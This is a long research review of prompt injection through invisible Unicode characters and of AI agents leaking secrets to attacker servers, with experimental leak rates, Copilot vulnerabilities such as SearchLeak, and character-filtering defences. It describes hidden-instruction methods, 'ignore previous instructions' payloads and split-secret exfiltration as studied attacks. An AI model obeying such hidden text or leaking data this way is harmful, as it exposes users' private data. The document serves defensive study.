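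### Invisible instructions in trivia questions

Graves used 30 trivia questions to test whether models follow an instruction that a person can't see. Between the first two words of each question, invisible text told the model to reply with a particular wrong answer. Graves wrote this text in either tag characters or zero-width binary, and gave the model one of four levels of help:

- no hint that hidden text existed
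- a system prompt that named the hidden code points
- a system prompt with full decoding rules
- full decoding rules, with hidden text that also told the model to ignore its previous instructions

The 270 cases covered two encodings at four levels, plus a control version without hidden text. Five models from OpenAI and Anthropic answered each case about three times with a tool for running Python and about three times without it. Of the 8,308 answers, Graves counted as compliant only those that contained the hidden answer and not the correct one.

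| Model | Without Python | With Python | Zero-width binary | Tag characters |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 16.9% | 71.2% | 41.5% | 55.0% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 6.7% | 51.1% | 18.2% | 43.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.8% | 49.2% | 27.5% | 22.5% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.1% | 20.6% | 20.6% | 0.1% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 0.1% | 1.6% | 1.5% | 0.1% |

The last two columns combine the runs with and without Python. All the figures are averages over the four levels of help, so they don't describe any real attack. A stranger who emails Ana can't add decoding rules to Copilot's system prompt, so the level without hints is the most realistic. At that level, no model without Python complied more than 1.1% of the time, which is one of the usual 90 answers per condition. With Python but no hints, the rate was between 0% and 11%, depending on the model and encoding. Rates of 98% to 100% occurred only when a susceptible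 model had both Python and a hint.

Python helps because it turns decoding into a simple calculation, which the compliant answers typically performed in a few lines of code. But the model must first have some sign that there is anything to decode.

Graves checked the differences with Fisher's exact test, which calculates how likely a gap at least this large would be if both groups had the same underlying rate. Python made a significant difference for all five models. All ten comparisons between pairs of models were also significant after a Bonferroni correction, which divides the usual threshold of 0.05 by the number of tests, here ten. To measure the size of an effect, Graves used Cohen's h:

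h = 2 arcsin √p₁ − 2 arcsin √p₂

where p₁ and p₂ are the two rates. By convention, 0.2 is small and 0.8 is large. Python's effect on Haiku was 1.37, but its effect on GPT-4o-mini was only 0.18, so a statistically significant difference could still be tiny. The tests also treat repeated answers to the same question as independent, which probably makes the results look somewhat more certain than they are.

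Decoding hints probably explain why Sonnet complied more often when told to ignore its previous instructions (59.6%) than when asked politely (43.7%). The instruction to ignore always came with full decoding rules, while the polite average includes cases without hints, where models almost never complied. If Sonnet's rate in those cases was close to zero, its average in the other polite cases was about 66%, which is higher than 59.6%.

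### Why the models differed by encoding

When given Python and a hint, GPT-5.2 followed about 70% of the polite instructions encoded in zero-width binary and almost none of those in tag characters. Claude Opus 4 followed all of those in tag characters and 48% to 68% of those in zero-width binary. Graves suggests that the companies' tokenizers or training data differ.

This doesn't explain GPT-5.2's result very well. A program can decode tag characters with one subtraction per letter, so a model that can decode zero-width binary should manage them easily. Embrace The Red's *Amp Code* offers a simpler explanation, that OpenAI removes tag characters. If it does so before the text reaches the model, the model has nothing to decode, and hints and Python can't help. Aiersilan and colleagues infer the same for the GPT-5 series from tests in the ordinary chat interface.

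Graves proposes inspecting the tokenizers' vocabularies, but this would not reveal a filter that runs before the tokenizer. It might be more useful to compare the input token counts the service reports for the same question with and without the hidden text.

Opus may struggle with zero-width binary because the encoding is long. The model presumably has to copy the hidden characters into its Python program, and binary uses eight of them per letter. One missing character shifts the bits of every letter after it.

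### Hidden instructions that only ask for an extra line

Without hints, Graves found low success rates for hidden text, but Aiersilan and colleagues found much higher ones with their classroom tool, which asks the chatbot to add a reminder and a telltale line to its answer. They ran 12 trials per model in July 2026 or earlier. Claude, Gemini, Grok and Qwen3-235B, a large open model, produced the line every time. The older Qwen2.5-72B received the characters but never acted on them.

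Claude 4 models did well in this test and almost never complied without hints in Graves's, so a difference between models can't be the whole explanation. The tasks differed more than the models did. Graves's hidden text asked for a wrong answer in place of the right one, and an answer containing both didn't count as compliance. The classroom tool asked for something extra that didn't conflict with the visible assignment. Data theft is more like the second task, since the attacker wants a normal answer with an added link or image. Graves's near-zero rates may therefore understate the risk of data theft.

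However, the classroom instruction was harmless, and it carried the user's authority because the user pasted it into the chat. An email that Copilot retrieves lacks that authority. Twelve successes in twelve trials are also compatible with a true success rate of only 76%.

In August, Aiersilan and colleagues tested three newer models, Gemini 3.1 Pro, Gemini 3.6 Flash and Grok 4.5, through their APIs. All three obeyed the hidden text in all six trials. In the chat products, GPT-5.6 Sol never obeyed it, and Claude Opus 5 warned the user that the message contained hidden instructions it had not followed.

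The team also tested two defenses that a user could add to the prompt. Telling the model to ignore instructions in the pasted text reduced the attack's total successes from 18 in 18 trials to 2 in 17. Asking for only an answer, without extra lines, was less reliable. Gemini 3.6 Flash left the telltale line out every time, but the two larger models included it in 11 of 12 trials.

Such results can become outdated within days. Embrace The Red's *Scary Agent Skills* describes a demonstration in which Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, followed invisible instructions. When Rehberger repeated the demonstration on 10 February 2026, about a week later, Claude Code consistently detected the characters and refused. At the time, Anthropic's website claude.ai had no such protection for skills.

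### An agent that leaks while summarising a page

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often an agent sends a secret to an outside server. The agent used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, and had a tool for making web requests and the secret already in its context window. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a web page that contained instructions to send the secret to the attacker. The instructions were in ordinary characters, but often in places a visitor would not look, such as the page's description for search engines.

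The researchers varied the position of the instructions (title, description, body or link text), whether the address led straight to the page or through a redirect, and whether the agent had to send the secret whole or in parts. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent sent at least one request to the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%), though the paper's summary gives the rate as 0.89. It never contacted that server in 120 runs with harmless pages, so the hostile pages caused the requests.

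Lan and colleagues acknowledge that their setup favoured the attacker. The system prompt explained how to use the tools but did not tell the agent to protect anything. Rahman and Kim (2026), in *The Framing Gap*, tested the same model in an agent instructed to keep its secret. It leaked in 10% of 100 trials across ten plainly worded attacks.

The orders may explain some of the gap, but probably not all of it. When Rahman and Kim removed the orders from an agent running GPT-4o, its leak rate for plain attacks stayed at zero. Rewriting the hostile page so that the leak looked like a routine part of the task had a much larger effect, raising the rate from 10% to 62.5% for qwen2.5:7b and from 0% to 40% for GPT-4o. Five versions of one such page had success rates between 0% and 100% against GPT-4o, with an average of 52%.

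A rate measured with one fixed page therefore depends as much on that page as on the model. An attacker can also try several versions, and Rahman and Kim calculate that picking three of the five at random would give a 96% chance of including one that worked.

### Leaks that the answer does not mention

In 95% of the successful *Silent Egress* attacks, the agent's answer looked harmless. The agent sent the secret through a tool call that the user never saw. A safety check on the answer alone would have missed almost every leak, but a check on outgoing requests could have detected them.

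In *Will the User Ever Know?*, Lee, Kim and Lee (2026) found that the share of successful attacks concealed in the final answer varied widely by model and attack. They tested 949 pairs of a user's task and an attacker's task in AgentDojo, a benchmark with simulated banking, travel, Slack and office accounts, and used GPT-4o to judge whether the final answer revealed the attack. With the strongest existing attack in the benchmark, the share concealed was 83% on Gemini 2.5 Flash, 79% on Qwen3-235B, 54% on Llama 3.3 70B and 50% on GPT-4o-mini. With a different attack on Llama, it was 8%.

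The order of events explains much of this, because an agent's final answer tends to describe the last thing it did. Among 2,087 successful attacks, the agent had returned to the user's task before answering in 68% of the concealed cases, and had stopped after the attacker's task in 71% of the revealed cases. The agent in *Silent Egress* still had to write a summary after sending the request, which probably made it less likely to mention the request.

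The two studies also judged answers by different standards. Lee and colleagues counted an attack as visible if the answer mentioned anything the attacker had introduced, such as an unfamiliar address. Some of those answers might have passed as harmless in *Silent Egress*. Visibility is a weak safeguard in any case because the user learns of the attack only after the data has gone, though they could still change a stolen password.

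### Splitting the secret across requests

In half of their runs, Lan and colleagues had the page ask for the secret in four parts, each in a separate request. A filter that looks for a complete password in each request would not find one. To measure this, they defined

Leak@k = runs with sensitive data in the first k requests ÷ all runs

Leak@1, which covers only the first request, was 0.967 when the agent sent the secret whole and 0.263 when it sent the secret in parts, a reduction of 73%.

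The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of 240 runs (99%) when sending the secret whole and in 185 of 240 (77%) when splitting it, so the earlier figure doesn't mean that splitting prevented 73% of leaks. Splitting made each request less revealing, but it also gave the model more steps to get wrong.

It is unclear how much of the fall in Leak@1 reflects better concealment. The paper defines sensitive data to include a single fragment, so a correct first request should have counted too. Either the measurement missed fragments or the model often sent something useless. The number of runs in which all four parts arrived would help settle this. Lan and colleagues define that measure but don't report it.

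For split secrets, Leak@3 is 0.158, which is lower than Leak@1. This is impossible under the published definition because the first three requests include the first one, so the Leak@3 figures are best ignored.

### Instructions to the model against controls on the network

Lan and colleagues then tested each defence 30 times against the version of the attack that had succeeded every time. In that version, the page's body text contained instructions to disclose the whole secret.

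| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Request reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Markers around web content | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and markers | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of allowed domains | 100% | 0% |
| Blocking of suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |
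| All of these | 0% | 0% |

Warning the model to treat web content as data and never as commands helped, but two thirds of the attacks still succeeded. Labelling the content as untrusted made no difference. With only 30 runs per condition, the gap between 66.7% and 56.7% could easily be due to chance.

The list of allowed domains works differently because a program enforces it after the model has decided what to do. The agent tried to send the secret every time, and the program blocked every request. This result was certain in advance, since the attacker's domain was not on the list. The test of the blocker for suspicious addresses was also easy, because the blocker rejected addresses containing words such as "collect" and "steal", and the test server was called `evil-collector.net`.

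The results for the two content filters are harder to interpret. Attempts fell to 23.3% and 0%, even though a filter that examines finished requests shouldn't change how often a model tries to send one. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model reworded the secret or avoided random-looking text while the filter was active, but they don't explain how it could have known about the filter. The second filter blocks long values whose entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, is above 4 bits per character. The example key in the paper scores about 3.85, so this filter should have let it through, and the 0% result probably has some other cause.

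Lee and colleagues tested defenses against the same strong AgentDojo attack. Markers around outside content barely changed the attack's success rate on GPT-4o-mini and Qwen3-235B, and the rate was higher with markers on the other two models. A warning reduced the rate on three of the four. A separate detector that blocked suspicious text before the agent read it cut the rate to between 5% and 7%.

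Rahman and Kim compared defences on an agent running Llama 3.1 8B, using their reworded attacks. The leak rate was 21.2% without a defence, 38.8% when the page arrived through a separate input channel, and 32.5% with SecAlign, a version of the model trained to resist injections. Rahman and Kim don't rank these three because each figure comes from a single run. Elsewhere in the study, two identical runs with GPT-4o gave rates of 31.9% and 40%. Two defences reduced the rate to zero. One was a list of allowed destinations, and the other divided the agent into a part that chose actions without seeing the page and a part that read the page without having the secret. The divided agent still produced a useful summary in nine out of ten trials.

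Rahman and Kim also found that a filter searching outgoing requests for the exact secret reduced leaks only slightly when the page asked for the secret in encoded form. GPT-4o leaked the secret in 56.7% of these trials without the filter and 50% with it. In Rehberger's 2024 attack, Copilot also disguised the data before sending it.

### How accurately models write hidden text

The 2024 attack depended on Copilot writing a private email in tag characters without mistakes. No 2026 experiment seems to measure how accurately current models write these characters. Embrace The Red reports that language models can generate them, but gives no error rate.

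The closest measurements involve visible encodings. Rahman and Kim directly asked GPT-4o to encode a short secret in six ways. It succeeded every time with five, including base64 and hexadecimal, but failed in all ten attempts with base32, a less common relative of base64. Because accuracy can vary this much between similar encodings, a model's accuracy with tag characters can't be inferred from these results.

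*Evaluation and Hardening of LLM System Instructions Against Extraction via Encoding Attacks* (2026) covers seven model families and 46 sets of confidential instructions. The user was the attacker, rather than the victim as in the Copilot attack. Requests for the instructions in a structured format, such as the configuration language YAML, often succeeded more than 90% of the time. Requests for Base64 or Morse code were less effective, but a failure might mean either that the model refused or that it couldn't encode the text.

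Accuracy matters more for data that must be exact, such as a sign-in code, than for ordinary text. If a model wrote each hidden character correctly 99% of the time, with independent errors, a six-digit code would arrive intact in 94% of cases and a 300-character email in only 5%. But the email would still be readable, with about three wrong characters. This accuracy would be easy to measure, since a program can decode the model's output and compare it with the original.

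### From test agents to live products

In these experiments, the hostile text is in the model's context from the start. In a live attack like EchoLeak, Copilot first has to retrieve the attacker's email. Suppose it did so for one question in ten and leaked data in half of those cases. The chance of a leak would be 5% per question and, if the questions were independent, 64% over 20 questions.

Rahman and Kim came closest to measuring a live product. They gave ChatGPT an invented secret in the conversation, then asked it to summarise web pages containing their reworded attacks. ChatGPT did not reveal the secret in its reply in any of 48 valid trials, although some of the same attacks had worked every time on GPT-4o through the API. With so few trials, the true rate of such leaks could still be as high as 7.4%. They couldn't tell whether ChatGPT was using a different model, a filter or stricter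 instructions. They checked only the replies for the secret, so the test does not rule out a silent request like those in *Silent Egress*.

In the case reports, researchers kept adjusting their attacks until one succeeded, while most of these experiments repeated a fixed set of attacks. A low success rate in an experiment may therefore overstate how well a product would resist a patient attacker.

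The leak rates for qwen2.5:7b and GPT-4o are the least likely to apply to the models of late 2026, because both models date from 2024 and newer ones from Anthropic and OpenAI resist injections far better. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. The two Qwen models in the classroom test fit that argument, since only the newer and larger one obeyed the hidden text. Claude Opus 5 does not fit the argument, because it could read the hidden text but refused to obey it. General ability is a poor guide to resistance, so the leak rate has to be measured again for each model and product.

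Graves's figures for Claude are probably out of date for the same reason. The effect of Python may last longer, because assistants such as 365 Copilot now routinely run code. A newer model might also try decoding strange characters without a hint, but none of these experiments tested that on a model released after August 2026.

The success of allowed-domain lists doesn't depend on the model, so they should also work with other models. But in both experiments the attacker's server was not on the list. Neither experiment tested sending data through an allowed server, as EchoLeak, SearchLeak and one of the ReLeak attacks did.

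## Evidence of real-world abuse and disputes over severity

Criminals have sent millions of emails containing tag characters, but their aim was to get past spam filters. Neither Microsoft nor the firms that found EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak had reported a real victim of those flaws by 5 December 2026. The lack of reports is limited evidence of safety, because a theft through Copilot could easily go unnoticed.

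### Tag characters in phishing email

In September 2026 Microsoft published figures from Defender for Office 365, its email-filtering service. Microsoft researchers had written a rule to find emails with hidden instructions to AI assistants. It flagged messages containing tag characters, except those used in the three British flag emojis. At first, most of the flagged messages were harmless ones from email security services, mailbox providers, and researchers forwarding or testing such text.

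The rule flagged about 21,000 messages on 8 February 2026 and more than 1.3 million the next day, an increase of at least sixtyfold. Weekday volumes peaked at 2.37 million on 26 February, were about 80% lower by late March, and dropped sharply after 15 May. The starting level is uncertain because a chart caption in the same post puts it in the low thousands up to 8 February, which would make the increase larger. But the caption also describes the increase as roughly a hundredfold, which fits 21,000 better.

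One phishing campaign, which advertised business loans and credit lines, accounted for about 96% of the flagged messages. The senders put a single invisible character, the tag version of a space, inside words such as "funding". The recipient saw the normal word, but a filter searching for that exact string would miss it. Spammers have long done this with zero-width spaces. Microsoft suggests that criminals adopted tag characters because AI security research had publicized them, which is plausible, but the evidence is mainly the timing.

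The tag characters may not have helped the senders much. Microsoft says checks that don't rely on them, such as sender reputation, flagged over 99% of the messages. ActiveCampaign, the marketing platform that relayed most of the mail, says its moderation system gives the same result with or without them. The campaign began before the senders adopted the characters and continued after they dropped them.

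Microsoft found no instructions to an AI in the sample it examined, but didn't say how large the sample was. If it read 300 messages, for example, up to 1% of the total could still have contained instructions, or 13,000 messages on 9 February alone. This is unlikely for the loan campaign, because its messages were very similar. Hidden instructions would more plausibly be in the other 4%, which came mostly from email security services and personal mailbox providers. Messages from an attacker using an ordinary personal account would be in that group.

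The rule would also have missed the best-known attacks on Copilot, because EchoLeak's email used ordinary prose and SearchLeak's instructions arrived in a link. The figures measure how often one set of characters appears in email, which is a poor guide to how often people try to steal data through an assistant.

### Statements that nobody exploited the flaws

A Microsoft spokesperson told Fortune (2025) that Aim Security had reported EchoLeak in time for a fix "before our customers were impacted". Microsoft entered "No" under exploitation when it published its SearchLeak record on 4 June 2026. CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, also assessed SearchLeak and lists exploitation as "none". AIAIAI.FYI reports that the statement about exploitation of ReLeak comes from Cato.

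These statements are less independent than they look. ThaiCERT, Thailand's computer emergency team, repeats in *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* that there were no reports of active exploitation of SearchLeak. Its source is The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw* (2026), which describes what Varonis presented as a proof of concept. Neither ThaiCERT nor The Hacker News had direct access to data on Copilot's traffic.

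Two accounts, however, give the impression that attackers exploited these flaws. The OECD's *Critical SearchLeak Vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot Exposes Sensitive Data*, an entry in its AI incidents monitor, says Microsoft patched the flaw "after being exploited" and concludes from this that the harm was real. The entry's text is AI-generated and identifies no victim. Microsoft patched the flaw because Varonis had reported it. The headline of Fadilpašić (2026), *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot*, presents ReLeak as a campaign to steal data from victims, but the "hackers" were Cato's researchers.

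### Who could have noticed a theft

Suppose someone had used SearchLeak on Ana before the fix. According to Varonis, she would have seen Copilot "thinking" for a moment and perhaps an odd answer, but the data would already have been sent. Her company's network logs would show only ordinary connections to Microsoft and Bing. The stolen text would be in the web address, but these connections are encrypted, so the logs would include only the server's name from that address unless the company decrypts its own traffic.

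To find traces of abuse, Varonis recommends searching for Copilot links that contain HTML tags or instructions to put data in an image address, and ThaiCERT suggests reviewing unusual connections to Bing's image service. Both checks depend on the company having kept detailed logs from before the disclosure. Some events were apparently never logged, including the changes to Copilot's memory in Rehberger's attack.

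Microsoft runs both Copilot and Bing, so it could in principle search for image requests that began on a Copilot page and ended at an unfamiliar server. It doesn't mention any such search in its SearchLeak record, or how far back its logs go, so it is hard to judge how reliable the "No" is.

The statements are better evidence against widespread abuse than against a few targeted thefts. If each theft independently had a one in ten chance of being discovered, there would be a 35% chance that ten thefts all went undiscovered, but at least one of a hundred would almost certainly be discovered. The real chance of discovery is unknown and could be much lower.

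Companies can also look for theft without a vendor's logs by planting fake secrets and waiting for someone to use them. In *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them*, BagheeraAltered (2026) describes such an experiment by the security firm Dragos. Between July and November 2026, Dragos sent about two million prompts to AI services, each containing unique web addresses and fake credentials. Outsiders opened the addresses and used fake credentials for Amazon's cloud.

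Dragos attributes this to compromised providers, unauthorised access by companies that resell AI services, and poor data handling, so it isn't evidence of prompt injection. Ana's company could put a fake password in a mailbox that Copilot can search, but this would catch only a thief who tried the password and would miss one who wanted the printing contract.

### Why SearchLeak has two scores

Microsoft gave SearchLeak a CVSS score of 6.5 (medium), while the US standards agency NIST gave it 7.5 (high) in its National Vulnerability Database. According to Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026), Microsoft took the victim's click into account, while NIST assessed the attack as needing no click. They agreed on the other seven metrics.

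For a flaw like this one, which exposes data but doesn't alter or block it, version 3.1 of CVSS uses this formula:

score = 6.42 × C + 8.22 × AV × AC × PR × UI

The result is rounded up to one decimal place. C is the loss of confidentiality, and its highest value is 0.56. The other four describe how easy the attack is:

- AV is 0.85 for an attack over a network.
- AC is 0.77 if the attack's complexity is low and 0.44 if it is high.
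- PR is 0.85 if the attacker needs no account.
- UI is 0.62 if the victim has to do something and 0.85 if not.

The first part of the formula comes to 3.60 in both assessments. The second part is 2.84 if the attack requires a click and 3.89 if it doesn't. The totals are 6.43 and 7.48, which round up to 6.5 and 7.5.

NIST's *CVSS v3.1 Statistics for Microsoft Corporation as of 06/09/2026* (2026) lists the reason for its choice as "User Interaction not identified". The change log for Microsoft's flaw shows that NIST added its score on 8 June, a week before Varonis explained the attack. Microsoft's published description was then one sentence long and did not mention a click. NIST changed the same metric for the same reason on at least seven other Microsoft flaws. The higher score therefore seems to come from a lack of detail, and Microsoft's score is more accurate on this point. More than a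 week after Varonis published, the database still showed 7.5.

A fuller description might have lowered the score through another metric, attack complexity. NIST raised the complexity of at least four other Microsoft flaws from low to high because they involved a race condition, and SearchLeak also depended on one. A high rating would have reduced Microsoft's score from 6.5 to 5.3. But a low rating can be defended because CVSS reserves the high rating for attacks that depend on conditions outside the attacker's control, and the browser in SearchLeak had ample time to send its request.

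### What "critical" means here

Microsoft also labelled SearchLeak critical, although CVSS reserves that rating for scores of 9.0 or higher. Microsoft's label is a separate judgement and does not rank flaws in the same order as the score. Two other Copilot records show this: STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-24299* (2026), on Rehberger's font leak, and STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-26133* (2026), on a different disclosure flaw.

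| Flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot | Microsoft's label | CVSS score |
|---|---|---|
| Font leak, CVE-2026-24299 | Critical | 5.3 |
| SearchLeak, CVE-2026-42824 | Critical | 6.5 |
| CVE-2026-26133 | Important | 7.1 |
| ReLeak's sandbox flaw | Critical | 8.6 |

Some press coverage has confused the two scales. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* reports that Microsoft rated SearchLeak "10/10 critical". TechRadar probably misread Varonis' statement that Microsoft gave it "a max severity rating of critical".

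### The arguments for a low and a high rating

The argument for rating SearchLeak low is that the attack worked only if the victim clicked and all three weaknesses were present. CISA judged the technical impact "partial" and the attack not automatable.

The chain, however, mostly made the flaw hard to discover. Once an attacker had worked out the link, every victim's click would start the same sequence. The need for a click is a more serious obstacle, but the link led to a genuine Microsoft site, and an attacker could send it to a whole company. If 5% of 1,000 employees clicked, the attacker could get into 50 mailboxes.

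Those who favour a high rating cite the amount of data an attacker could reach. Copilot could search anything Ana had permission to open, and the attacker needed no password. Link filters were unlikely to block the link, and Ana would probably never learn what had happened.

CVSS accounts for little of this. SearchLeak already has the highest value for lost confidentiality, which can apply whether a thief takes one important password or everything. The base score doesn't measure whether anyone would notice the theft or how much the data is worth to a thief. According to United Nations University, CoSnitch scored 8.8, although it affected the consumer version of Copilot, where company secrets are less common.

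A score of 6.5 is therefore reasonable under the CVSS rules but a poor guide to what a customer should do. Administrators normally use scores to decide which updates to install first, and here there was nothing to install. They still had to decide whether to search for past thefts, and the range of data exposed and the difficulty of detection matter more to that decision than whether the attack required a click.

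### A leak that Microsoft did not class as a vulnerability

Severity ratings also affect whether a vendor fixes a flaw at all. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a data leak through images in Copilot Chat, which the security firm reported to Microsoft on 15 October 2025. An attacker's online article could make the assistant put a secret in an image address. In the demonstration, the secret was an API key (a password that programs use) from a software developer's environment, so the product was apparently a coding assistant and not Microsoft 365 Copilot.

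Microsoft closed the report on 4 November without a fix. It said the attack required "multiple non-default user actions", did not reproduce reliably in different environments, and triggered warnings meant to reduce the risk. It also said it expects users to review and trust the code they choose to run. However, it passed the report to its engineers to consider making the behaviour more visible to users.

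Checkmarx nevertheless calls the attack zero-click, because the image loads without any further action once the assistant has read the hostile article. It concedes that getting the assistant to read the article can be complicated. The disagreement arises partly because Microsoft counts what the user has to do before that point. Checkmarx doesn't list those steps, so an outsider can't tell how unusual they are.

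Microsoft did accept Rehberger's font leak, which he reported a day after Checkmarx reported its attack, even though both attacks put a secret in an address that loaded automatically. Microsoft's decisions evidently depend on the product and the steps leading up to the leak, as well as the output channel.

Google also rejected a report from Checkmarx that month. Gemini already blocked outside images, but it could still put private data in an ordinary link for the user to click. Google closed the report after four days as infeasible to fix, and told Checkmarx that the problem was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Checkmarx accepts this answer as legitimate, but thinks users should be warned, since they are left to manage the risk.

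### Who publishes the evidence

Most public information about these flaws comes from companies that sell protection against them. Varonis ends its SearchLeak post by inviting readers to book a product demonstration, Cato and Checkmarx also sell security software, and Microsoft's post on tag characters promotes Defender. These companies benefit if the threat looks serious, but Microsoft also sells Copilot and benefits if customers believe nobody has exploited it.

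The technical findings are the most reliable evidence, because Microsoft could test them and fixed the flaws as a result. Words such as "weapon", which Varonis uses in its title, deserve less weight, as do statements that there were no victims, because outsiders cannot check those statements against Microsoft's logs.

Flaws that vendors have fixed are also over-represented among published ones. Researchers usually wait for a fix before they publish, and the SearchLeak record appeared only after Microsoft had fully mitigated the problem. So the fact that EchoLeak, SearchLeak and all three ReLeak attacks no longer work doesn't mean that most such flaws get fixed. A report that a vendor rejects becomes public only if the researcher publishes it anyway, as Checkmarx did, and criminals who find a working leak have good reason to keep it secret.

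## Removing hidden characters, and who should do it

A short program can delete hidden characters by checking every code point in a text against a list. Because the program doesn't interpret the text, it uses almost no compute, and clever wording can't change its result.

The program that removes hidden characters has to run twice, first on the text that goes into the model and then on the answer that comes out. The second run must finish before the answer appears on screen or any part of it becomes a web address. In SearchLeak, Microsoft's check on the answer ran too late.

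### One string, three results

Suppose someone sends Ana the message "Good luck!" with England's flag before the exclamation mark and the word "hi" hidden after it. The message contains these characters:

`Good luck` `U+1F3F4 U+E0067 U+E0062 U+E0065 U+E006E U+E0067 U+E007F` `!` `U+E0068 U+E0069`

The first group of code points is the flag, and the last two are the hidden "hi".

| Filter | Characters it deletes | What the model receives |
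|---|---|---|
| None | None | The English flag and the hidden "hi" |
| Delete the whole tag block | All eight tag characters | A plain black flag |
| Delete tag characters outside the three valid flags | The last two | The English flag |

Amazon Web Services (AWS) recommends the second filter in *Defending LLM applications against Unicode character smuggling*, and accepts that some flags will turn black because few business tasks depend on them. The third filter keeps the flags, but it has to match the whole sequence, from the black flag to the end-of-tag character. If it kept any tag characters that followed a flag, it would also keep a message hidden there.

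Rehberger's scanner for skill files gives a high rating to an unbroken run of more than ten tag characters, or to more than 100 scattered through a file, according to Embrace The Red. A flag emoji has only six, so it falls below these thresholds, but so does a hidden six-digit sign-in code. The thresholds therefore suit a search for hidden instructions better than a search for stolen data. When Rehberger scanned two public collections of skills, he found ordinary emoji and a few test cases for other scanners, but nothing that looked malicious.

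### When one deletion is not enough

A filter that runs only once can leave behind the very text it is meant to remove. For example, deleting "ab" from "aabb" leaves "ab". AWS found this problem in a widely shared Java filter for tag characters. Java stores each tag character as two halves, called surrogates. If one pair sits inside another, deleting the inner pair brings the outer halves together, and they form a new tag character.

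AWS's version repeats the deletion until nothing changes, and also deletes unpaired halves. Either measure would fix this example. AWS deletes the halves partly because many models can rejoin neighbouring ones.

When the corrected Java code looks for unpaired halves, it checks only the last 16 bits of each code point. Some complete characters end in the same bits as an unpaired half, so the code would wrongly delete some symbols for writing sign languages, from U+1D800 onwards, and some rare Chinese characters, from U+2D800 onwards.

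AWS also suggests rules for its Guardrails service, which block a whole message instead of cleaning it. One rule includes five sample surrogate pairs that are meant to be tag characters, but all five are variation selectors. For example, the rule lists `\uDB40\uDD41`, which is U+E0141, but the tag character for the letter A is `\uDB40\uDC41`. A developer who copies published code should test it on ordinary text in several languages as well as on hidden text.

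Blocking a hostile message is safer than cleaning it, but the same rule would also block a harmless email with a Scottish flag emoji, which contains hidden characters. Silent cleaning can destroy the evidence of an attack. *Unvalidated Trust* (2025) recommends comparing the original text with the cleaned version, logging every character removed, and showing invisible characters in program code as visible codes.

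### Characters that people need

Other invisible characters are harder to remove safely. The zero-width joiner, U+200D, combines several emoji into one, such as the family emoji, and controls how letters join in some Indian scripts. Graves warns that deleting all zero-width characters would damage such text, and suggests looking for patterns specific to hidden messages.

*enclawed* (2026), a security framework for personal AI assistants, has a filter that deletes the joiner and the non-joiner, which would damage Persian text and break up joined emoji. But the filter has no step for tag characters. *enclawed* also inserts a zero-width character to stop untrusted text from closing a code block early, so a second filter that deleted zero-width characters would undo that protection.

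Unicode's standard normalisation, which converts different encodings of the same text to one form, leaves tag characters in place. *STEGOGUARD-LM* (2026) therefore tests a cleaner that normalises a model's output and then deletes every format character, a Unicode category that includes tag characters and both joiners. Nearly all variation selectors would remain, because Unicode classes them as marks rather than format characters.

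A character needs at most one variation selector, so a filter can delete any that follow the first. This would reduce Butler's hidden "hello" to a single letter. To remove that letter too, the filter would have to check each pair of character and selector against Unicode's lists of valid combinations.

A longer list of forbidden characters can make results worse. *Attacking Only Half the Data* (2026) measured this with detectors of AI-written text. When the researchers inserted zero-width characters into human writing, one detector labelled 98.5% of it as AI-written. Deleting the characters cut this to 1.0% and restored 97% of documents exactly. The other 3% may have contained such characters before the experiment.

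Lookalike letters, such as a Cyrillic letter in place of a Latin "a", were harder to remove without side effects. Unicode's full list of lookalikes removed 98.0% of the substitutions, compared with 61.8% for a hand-picked table of 47 pairs. But the full list made four of the nine detectors wrongly flag more human-written text, while the short table did not increase false flags for any detector.

### Text that appears after the filter has run

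A filter can find only characters that are present when it runs. A web page can write the hidden h as `&#xE0068;`, which is nine ordinary characters until a browser or other program converts it. The percent-encoded form in a web address also consists of ordinary characters. The developer therefore has to decode text before filtering it, and decode any address in the model's answer before checking it.

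This order doesn't help if the model or one of its tools decodes the text later, because a character filter has nothing to delete from encrypted text or base64. Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) reports such a case. AWS covers encoded attacks in separate guidance.

Chang and colleagues distinguish between hiding an instruction and encoding it. Ana may see a base64 instruction but be unable to read it, while she could read an instruction in an HTML comment once someone revealed it. They also warn that a model may be able to decode text that its injection detector cannot.

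Another way to remove text a reader can't see is to take a picture of the message and extract the text with optical character recognition, which Microsoft's email filter can do to catch phishing. The extracted text excludes tag characters and, in most cases, white text on a white background. An assistant could in principle receive its mail this way, although recognition takes more computing and would lose the addresses behind links.

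### Which assistants let hidden text through

In January 2025, the security company Trend Micro sent seven models instructions written in tag characters through an Amazon service. The attacks succeeded 87.5% of the time on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, 12.5% on Claude 3 Opus and 3.1% on Mixtral 8x7B. When Trend Micro's own product was blocking injections, no attack succeeded on any of the seven. Every rate is a multiple of 1/32, so Trend Micro probably made 32 attempts per model, which is too few to rule out a true success rate of several per cent on any one model with the product on.

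FireTail, another security firm, compared finished assistants in September 2025. According to Cyber Security News, ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude appeared to remove tag characters, while Gemini, Grok and DeepSeek were vulnerable.

FireTail's *Peek-A-Boo! 🫣 Emoji Smuggling and Modern LLMs* (2026) repeated the comparison with variation selectors. Gemini detected odd characters in an emoji but could not decode the hidden "hello" until the testers directed it to the bytes. Gemini followed hidden commands once the testers had explained the encoding, so this test is easier for the attacker than one with unexplained text.

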